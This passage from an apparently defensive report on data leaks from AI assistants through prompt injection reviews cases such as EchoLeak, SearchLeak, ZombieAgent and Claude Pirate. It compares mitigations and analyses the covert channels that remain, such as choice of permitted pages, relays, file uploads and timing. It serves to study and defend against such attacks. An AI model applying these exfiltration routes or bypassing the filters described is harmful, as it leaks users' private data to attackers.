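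| Search outgoing traffic for private data | None listed | The zero-click leak |

Reddy and Gujral base these judgements on analysis. They state that they didn't reproduce the attack or run any experiments, although one sentence in the paper refers to results "in our tests". Some of the judgements are debatable. They rate the use of internal sources by default as failing against the zero-click leak, but elsewhere write that EchoLeak "fails by design" if Copilot never uses strangers' emails to answer questions about internal projects. The second judgement seems right, because the model would never have read the attacker's email.

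They may also be too optimistic about the strict Content Security Policy they recommend, which allows only the company's own hosts, without wildcards. The relay in EchoLeak was one of Microsoft's own services, so such a policy could still have allowed it.

One signed proxy design adds an expiry time to every address, so an attack like CamoLeak would work only until the addresses the attacker had collected expired.

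Despite these problems, their analysis agrees with the eBay experiment that restricting the request can stop the leak even after a hijack.

### Can a person approve each action?

Reddy and Gujral expect human review to stop more steps of EchoLeak than any other mitigation, but Anthropic's data on how people respond to approval requests is much less encouraging.

Anthropic paid for a study of 1,053 professional testers who worked on coding tasks. Partway through each session, the software showed the tester a clearly dangerous command and asked for permission to run it. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more requests.

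The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a real developer would. Anthropic was also about to make auto mode the default instead of manual approval, and the study supported that decision. Still, Anthropic's data from actual use is similar, with Claude Code users approving 97% of permission requests, although most of these are presumably harmless.

The same users reject 39% of the plans that Claude asks them to approve. Plans come up less often than permission requests, and users can judge from a plan whether Claude has understood the task. A web address containing a long code is much harder for them to judge. Lan and colleagues make a similar point about requests that an attacker disguises as a routine connection check. Vendors should therefore ask for approval only on a few important decisions.

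### Blocking outgoing requests

Egress control can stop a leak even if nobody recognises the attack, but the user loses some features. Willison likes that OpenAI's Lockdown Mode does this with fixed rules instead of another AI model, which an attacker might also fool. He also infers from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's normal settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's head of information security, recommends the mode for people at elevated risk and says it isn't meant for everyone, because it makes ChatGPT less useful.

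A company also needs to check that its egress control works. ReLeak describes getting data out of Copilot's supposedly isolated code sandbox. A developer can test a sandbox by running a program inside it that tries to contact an outside server by every available method. If any attempt succeeds, the sandbox isn't secure, though it may still be insecure even if they all fail.

Allowlists have the same weakness for agents as for images, because a permitted service may accept data from anyone. PromptArmor has reported leaks from Anthropic's Claude Cowork and Google's Antigravity, which both limited connections to a default list of domains. Neither leak has a known fix.

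### Tracking where data came from

Web addresses and secret-looking words are only clues to a leak. Software could instead record which information came from strangers and stop it from influencing risky actions. Lan and colleagues suggest adapting taint tracking, an established technique for finding flaws in ordinary programs:

1. The software labels text from a web page as tainted when it arrives.
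2. The label spreads to anything that the text influences, such as the address in a request.
3. Before the agent sends a request, opens a file or uses a password, the software looks for the label.
4. If it finds one, it blocks the action, asks the user or records the event for later review.

Labels could catch a leak that sends only a few characters at a time, because they don't depend on what the data looks like. However, Lan's team didn't build a labelling system, and spreading labels correctly is hard because a model mixes everything in its context. The software can't determine which words influenced which part of the answer. If it labels everything the model writes after reading one web page, just to be safe, it will block a lot of ordinary work.

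*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) describes CaMeL, a system that avoids some of this problem. One model sees only the user's request and writes a short program to carry it out. Another model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text and extracts the information the program needs. Ordinary software runs the program and tracks where each value came from. For example, if the user asks to send a document to Bob, a stranger's email can't add a new step that sends it to somebody else.

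CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks in a standard test, compared with 84% for an unprotected system. Some users would accept that loss for the extra security, but a vendor also has to rebuild its agent around the design and write rules for how the agent may use each kind of data.

### What Google and Microsoft have published

In June 2025, Google described Gemini's defences. Google trains the model on attacks, uses classifiers to detect hostile instructions in emails and files, and adds reminders to the prompt to keep the model on the user's task. Gemini requires confirmation before some risky actions, such as deleting a calendar event, and notifies users when it has blocked an attack.

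Gemini doesn't display images from external addresses, so, as Google pointed out, EchoLeak's image attack couldn't work on Gemini. This rule is stronger than allowing a list of trusted outside hosts, which can go out of date. But Google still has to make sure none of the hosts it treats as internal can fetch other addresses. The rule also doesn't cover the clicked-link leak that Google declined to fix.

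Microsoft described its own defences in July 2025. They include hardened system prompts, a classifier called Prompt Shields, requests for user consent, and permissions that limit what data Copilot can reach. Microsoft also uses fixed rules to block known ways of leaking data, including Markdown images. Its researchers have developed FIDES, which tracks untrusted data in an agent.

Another of its methods, spotlighting, marks untrusted text so that the model can distinguish it from instructions. For example, the software might put a special character between the words of an email. Hines and colleagues at Microsoft reported in 2024 that spotlighting reduced successful attacks from more than 50% to below 2%. The tags in the eBay experiment had no effect, perhaps because they marked only the beginning and end of the text, or because the model was too small to use them. Neither result shows how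 well spotlighting works against an attacker who has studied it.

Google and Microsoft describe many of the same layers of defence, but SearchLeak and one of the ReLeak attacks still got data out of Copilot through Bing. Removing Bing from the image policy would have closed that route, while another classifier would only have made the attacks less likely to succeed.

### The defences compared

| Defence | What it stops | Known failure | Cost to users |
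|---|---|---|---|
| Training the model | Many injected instructions, whatever the attacker wants | Opus 5 still failed 2.0% of the time after 15 attempts | Very little, unless the model ignores legitimate requests |
| Classifier on input | Hostile text it recognises | EchoLeak's email, which seemed to address a person | Occasional false alarms |
| Sanitiser on output | Images and links the developer anticipated | EchoLeak's overlooked links, SearchLeak's streaming race | Missing pictures and links |
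| Content Security Policy | Browser requests to hosts not on the list | Relays, expired domains, requests made by servers | Pictures from other hosts don't load |
| Image proxy with signed addresses | Image addresses the model makes up | CamoLeak's choice among signed addresses | Unsigned pictures don't load |
| Check on exact addresses | Addresses composed from private data | Choice among known addresses, traffic that skips the check | Warnings or refusals for some harmless pages |
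| User approval | Actions the user recognises as dangerous | Testers approved 86% of dangerous commands | Frequent interruptions |
| Egress control | Requests to destinations not on the list | ReLeak's escape from the code sandbox | Less browsing and fewer connected services |
| Tracking untrusted data | Risky actions that a stranger's text has influenced | Labels can spread to nearly everything the model writes | Some tasks fail or need approval |

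An image proxy without signatures is missing from the table because, like Gmail's, it still passes the whole image address to the sender's server.

### An assistant that reads email and shows pictures

Suppose a company builds an assistant that answers questions about a user's mailbox in a chat window. The assistant can show pictures and links but can't browse the web, run code or send messages. Anybody can email the user, so the company should expect someone to eventually hijack the assistant. Private data could then leave through a picture or a clicked link.

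The simplest way to prevent the image leak is to block external images, as Gemini does. The assistant could still show photographs attached to emails, because the company already has those files. Users would lose the images in newsletters and other messages that load them from outside servers.

If the company wants to keep those pictures, it can prevent the model from choosing any image address:

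1. When an email arrives, the company's server downloads the pictures in it and stores copies, before the assistant reads the email.
2. Each copy gets a number, and the model uses that number to include the picture in an answer.
3. The renderer inserts the stored copy and discards any image address the model writes.
4. The Content Security Policy allows images only from a host that serves stored copies and can't fetch anything else.

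The sender chose the original address before the assistant read anything, so the download can't contain data that the assistant found in the mailbox. The sender still learns that the email arrived, as with a tracking pixel. But if the server downloads the pictures in every email, the sender can't tell whether either the user or the assistant ever opened that email.

The renderer and the policy each cover gaps in the other. If a developer overlooks an unusual image syntax, the policy still stops the browser from contacting the attacker's server. If someone later adds a relay to the policy, the renderer still discards any address that would use it. The renderer must apply its rule while the answer is streaming, because checking only at the end would recreate the flaw that made SearchLeak possible.

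The renderer can make a link clickable only if that exact address appears in one of the user's emails. A hijacked assistant then can't add a password to the end of a clickable link. Users lose little, since an assistant that summarises email seldom needs to compose a new address. But an attacker could send an email containing many different links and have the assistant choose one based on something in the mailbox. A click would then reveal a small amount of information.

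| Possible leak | Combination that closes it | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Picture on the attacker's server | Stored copies and a Content Security Policy | A leak if both fail |
| Picture through a relay | Stored copies and an image host that can't fetch addresses | A leak if the renderer fails and somebody adds a relay to the policy |
| Private data in a clicked link | Exact match with an address in the user's email | The choice among links the attacker supplied |
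| Page request, if the company adds browsing | Exact-address check on the server | The choice among pages the check allows |
| Link preview, if the assistant posts to Slack | Both preview settings off | Links that people click |
| Request from a program, if the assistant runs code | Sandbox with no network access | Flaws in the sandbox |

The company should still use a model that resists injection, because these restrictions don't prevent a hijacked assistant from lying. Without using an image or link, it could tell the user that a supplier has changed its bank details, and the user might send money to the attacker. Model training and input classifiers are the defences most likely to prevent this, and the company could also show which email each claim came from.

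The display restrictions are easier to test than the model because a developer doesn't need to hijack the assistant. The developer can give the renderer prepared answers containing images and links in every format it supports, then watch the browser's network requests while the answers stream in. Any request to an outside server is a failure. The company can run this test automatically whenever it changes the renderer, and it doesn't need new attacks each time it changes the model.

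## Which covert channels remain hard to close?

Checking exact addresses stops a hijacked agent from writing private data into an address, but the agent still chooses which permitted pages to open. If those choices depend on private data, an attacker who runs the website can learn something about that data from the server's log. This is a covert channel, a way of passing information through a mechanism not meant to carry it. Computer scientists were trying to close such channels decades before language models existed.

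### The confinement problem

In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) considered a customer who runs someone else's program on confidential data. The program needs the data to do its job, but the customer wants to be sure that it doesn't pass the data to the program's owner. Lampson noted that wrong results at least give the customer evidence of a problem, whereas a leak usually leaves no sign.

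A program that can't send messages can still leak data by changing anything an outsider can observe. For example, the program's owner has to receive a copy of the customer's bill, so the program could hide information in the amount. It could also vary how heavily it uses the computer, and another program running at the same time could detect the changes in speed.

Lampson's simplest remedy was total isolation, in which the confined program never calls any other program, but he called this "quite impractical". Another was to let the customer decide what goes into each channel, for example by working out the bill from a published price list. If closing a channel completely was too burdensome, the customer could limit how much information it carried. Steven Lipner examined the same problem in 1975 and, according to lecture notes from Purdue University, concluded that closing covert channels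 seemed to impose an "unreasonable performance penalty".

With an AI assistant, the user is the customer, the hijacked agent is the confined program and the attacker takes the owner's place. Once the agent is following a stranger's instructions, the honesty of the company that built it makes little difference. Total isolation is even less practical than it was in 1973, because a browsing agent's job is to request pages from strangers' servers.

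### How much can a permitted request reveal?

A bit is the amount of information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely. If an agent opens one of N permitted addresses, its choice conveys at most log₂ N bits, which is 1 bit for two addresses and 5 bits for 32. If it makes k requests, its choices convey at most k × log₂ N bits.

A six-digit login code has a million possible values, so it contains about 20 bits. A page of text contains many thousands of bits. The table lists the smallest number of requests that could reveal each secret in full, assuming 10,000 bits for the page.

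| Addresses to choose from | Most bits per request | Six-digit code | Page of text |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 requests | 10,000 requests |
| 32 | 5 | 4 requests | 2,000 requests |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 requests | 1,000 requests |

A real attack might need more requests, because the model can make mistakes. Even so, an agent that reads dozens of pages for one answer could make four extra requests without anyone noticing, but 2,000 requests to one website should stand out. Restricting an agent to known addresses therefore protects documents much better than it protects codes.

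The bound covers only which addresses the agent opens, not whether it opens any. Metere (2026) points out in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* that the choice between sending and not sending can always leak one bit.

A single leaked bit can harm someone. *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* (Schroeder de Witt, 2026) gives the example of whether a person has a particular diagnosis. Limiting the number of bits limits the harm only if the sender can't use them to reveal the most damaging fact. An ordinary program doesn't select parts of a medical record by importance, but a capable AI agent can work out which part matters.

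Schroeder de Witt's argument is theoretical and concerns agents that share enough background knowledge to settle on the same damaging fact without discussing it. Prompt injection makes this easier because the attacker can tell the agent which question to answer.

### Leaks through permitted addresses in ChatGPT and Claude

After ShadowLeak, the email attack on Deep Research, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding anything to the URLs it opened. Radware's *ZombieAgent*, published in January 2026, describes a slower leak that this restriction did not prevent. Radware reported the leak on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI tightened the restriction and had fixed the leak by 16 December.

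Claude's chat app had a comparable leak, since fixed, through the links it followed on Ayush Paul's website. In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) recounts that he first asked Claude to put his name into a URL, but Anthropic's rule blocked the request. The links got past the rule, and the visible conversation looked ordinary.

In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb estimates that Paul's attack leaked about 143 bits in roughly 30 requests. That is enough for seven login codes. According to dyb, the leaked details included Paul's home city, which he had never told Claude. Claude had inferred it from the name of a school hackathon. A user searching Claude's saved memories for private facts to delete could easily miss one like that.

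OpenAI's current check leaves a similar channel open, because the choice of which public address to load can still reveal data. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI acknowledges this in its technical paper, and Rehberger described the idea in 2023. He thinks leaking a few bits "still seems straightforward", because anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably already has enough pages in the index.

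The attacker also has to see the visits, so the pages must be on a website whose logs the attacker can read. Rehberger hadn't recently tested ChatGPT when he wrote this, so his post identifies a gap in the design but doesn't demonstrate a leak from the current product. He still calls the check "a significant improvement", and the table above supports him, since one request could carry a whole paragraph before the check.

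### What it costs to slow the leak

Rehberger suggests two ways to limit repeat visits. The vendor could cache each page for a few minutes, so that a second visit in that time doesn't reach the website, or it could stop the agent from opening the same address twice in one session.

If an agent can open each of 32 addresses only once, it can leak about 120 bits through which addresses it opens and in what order, however long the session lasts. That is far too little for a page of text but enough for six login codes, and the limit is higher if the attacker has more pages in the index. The restriction also interferes with tasks that depend on fresh information, such as repeatedly checking whether a sold-out concert has new tickets.

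Anthropic caches the pages that its web fetch tool retrieves, and warns developers that the content may be out of date. The cache is there for speed, and Anthropic may change how it works, so developers can't rely on it for security.

A request budget limits the total number of pages an agent can fetch. Developers can set one for Anthropic's tool, but it applies to each API call separately, so a long conversation can far exceed it. Even within a budget, an agent that makes 50 requests, each to one of 32 addresses, can convey at most 250 bits, which is too little to leak the page of text but enough to leak the code. To protect the code, the agent would have to stop after three requests, too few for most research tasks. A separate budget for each website would be less restrictive, but it would make long manuals hard to read, and an attacker could get around it by registering more websites.

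Metere proposes giving each destination a budget, measured in bits, that refills over time. Software estimates how much hidden data each outgoing message could carry and deducts that amount from the budget. When the budget runs out, the software delays or cancels further suspicious messages. Metere tested a working version of the wider system against fifteen attack programs, but not in a commercial assistant. The estimates cover what is inside a message, so a vendor would need a different way to estimate how much data the choice of a web page could carry.

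dyb also suggests letting an agent follow links only on websites the user has named in the conversation. The user would have to confirm each site once, and an unfamiliar website could not lead the agent through its pages. But people often use a research agent to find websites they don't know about. Another suggestion is to watch for long runs of similar requests to one site, though dyb admits that ordinary multi-page documentation would set off false alarms. This monitoring would be least useful for protecting a login code, which may take only a few requests to leak.

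Keeping login codes away from the agent would probably work better. They have a recognisable format and usually expire within minutes, so an email assistant could hide recent ones from the model with little inconvenience to the user. A diagnosis is much harder to hide this way because it has no fixed wording.

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode restricts browsing far more than any of these limits. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* explains that the agent can read only cached pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. The attacker's server then can't see which pages the agent reads or how many. This is close to Lampson's total isolation, except that the agent has a stored copy of part of the web.

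Lockdown Mode protects against data theft by heavily restricting ChatGPT. OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* warns that search results may be stale or missing. The mode also turns off Deep Research and agent mode, and stops ChatGPT from retrieving images from the web or downloading files for analysis. The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* concludes that ChatGPT loses most of what makes its agent and research features useful.

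### Permitted services that accept outside content

Counting the bits each address can carry doesn't help if a permitted service accepts whole files. In 2025, Rehberger showed in Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* that a hijacked Claude could copy a past conversation to an attacker's account on Anthropic's file service. The trusted host stored the data until the attacker collected it, rather than forwarding a request as in the earlier relay attacks.

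Lampson's list of leaks includes this one, in which a program writes a file for its owner to pick up later. He thought such storage channels were fairly easy to block once someone had found them all, and Lipner agreed that they could be closed without much difficulty. Here, a sandbox could refuse uploads to any account except the user's own. A list of permitted hosts can't make that distinction, because the user's account and the attacker's are at the same host.

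Anthropic restricted access to the file service after Rehberger's report, according to dyb. After a vulnerability report in June 2026, it also removed Hugging Face, an AI platform where anyone can publish files, from the domains that Claude Code could contact without asking. Oasis Security's *Claude.ai Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration* reports another leak from Claude's chat app, and nobody has confirmed that it is completely fixed.

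dyb lists six leaks from Claude products between October 2025 and July 2026, and argues that new integrations create possible channels faster than patches can close them. Six cases are too few to measure either rate. Still, each connected app does give a hijacked agent more things to change, and an outsider may be able to see some of those changes.

In its advice to workplace administrators, OpenAI distinguishes actions that only read from a connected app from those that write to it, such as posting a comment. It recommends leaving a write action off, even in a trusted app, unless the administrator can be sure that attackers can't see the result. Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically disable every app in a managed workplace account, so administrators have to make these decisions themselves. This may be difficult, because a private document can become public later if a colleague shares it.

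### Connections the user approves

Restricting an agent to a set of known addresses limits what it can leak, but a user can undo that protection by approving an address outside the set. If the user clicks through OpenAI's warning about an unverified address, that address can contain any text the agent wrote into it. A single approval might therefore leak more data than the agent could by choosing which public page to load hundreds of times.

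A single approval can cover more than one address. In Canvas, ChatGPT's workspace for writing and code, users can normally approve network access for a program that ChatGPT wrote. They then have to judge what the program will send, which is harder than inspecting a link. Lockdown Mode removes this option.

However, people with personal accounts can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat. They are most likely to do this when a task needs the live web, which often means reading pages written by strangers. It would be safer to use that chat only for web research and keep private files and connected accounts out of it.

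### Apps and features without the fix

A vendor may know how to close a channel and still leave it open in some of its products. OpenAI's first URL check didn't cover its phone and Mac apps. Lockdown Mode doesn't affect network access in Codex, so turning it on for ChatGPT doesn't protect confidential files that the user also gives to Codex.

Staff tools also need the fix. Developers investigate conversations that went wrong in log viewers, such as the OpenAI one described in PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs Unpatched Data Exfiltration*, so they are especially likely to open hostile output there.

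Lampson assigned enforcement to the supervisor, the part of the operating system that every program depends on. An AI company could similarly send all its agents' requests through one gateway that refuses anything it hasn't checked. At the moment, a new feature that lacks the URL check works normally in testing, so the team may not notice the omission. With the gateway, the feature's pages wouldn't load, and the team would have to fix the problem before launch.

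A gateway on the vendor's servers can't control images that an app on the user's computer fetches directly. To control those, the vendor would need every app to use the same renderer, with outside images blocked unless a developer deliberately turns them on.

### Timing and order

Even if every app checked every address correctly, a hijacked agent could still leak data by choosing when to make its requests and in what order. Lampson argued that a program could get information out by varying its effect on a shared computer, however small that effect was, though the channel might be very slow.

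*AgenticOS* (2026) proposes an operating system for AI agents that defends against such signals. The system releases outgoing requests only in fixed time windows and pads outputs to standard sizes so that their length reveals less. *AgenticOS* accepts that covert channels can't be eliminated, and aims to make the remaining ones slow enough to monitor and difficult to exploit.

Metere notes that random delays only reduce what an agent can convey through timing, while sending requests at a constant rate closes the channel. But a constant rate adds delay and traffic. If an agent reads 40 pages one after another and waits up to five seconds to send each request, the user could wait more than three extra minutes. The system would also have to send dummy requests when the agent had nothing to fetch, because a gap would convey information.

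So far, timing is a theoretical problem for chat assistants. None of the product leaks described here relied on timing alone, and attackers have had much faster routes. Ordinary internet delays also blur the signal, and Rehberger found that requests could arrive out of order while working on image leaks in 2023. Most vendors would protect their users more by extending existing address checks to every app than by slowing all browsing to a fixed pace.
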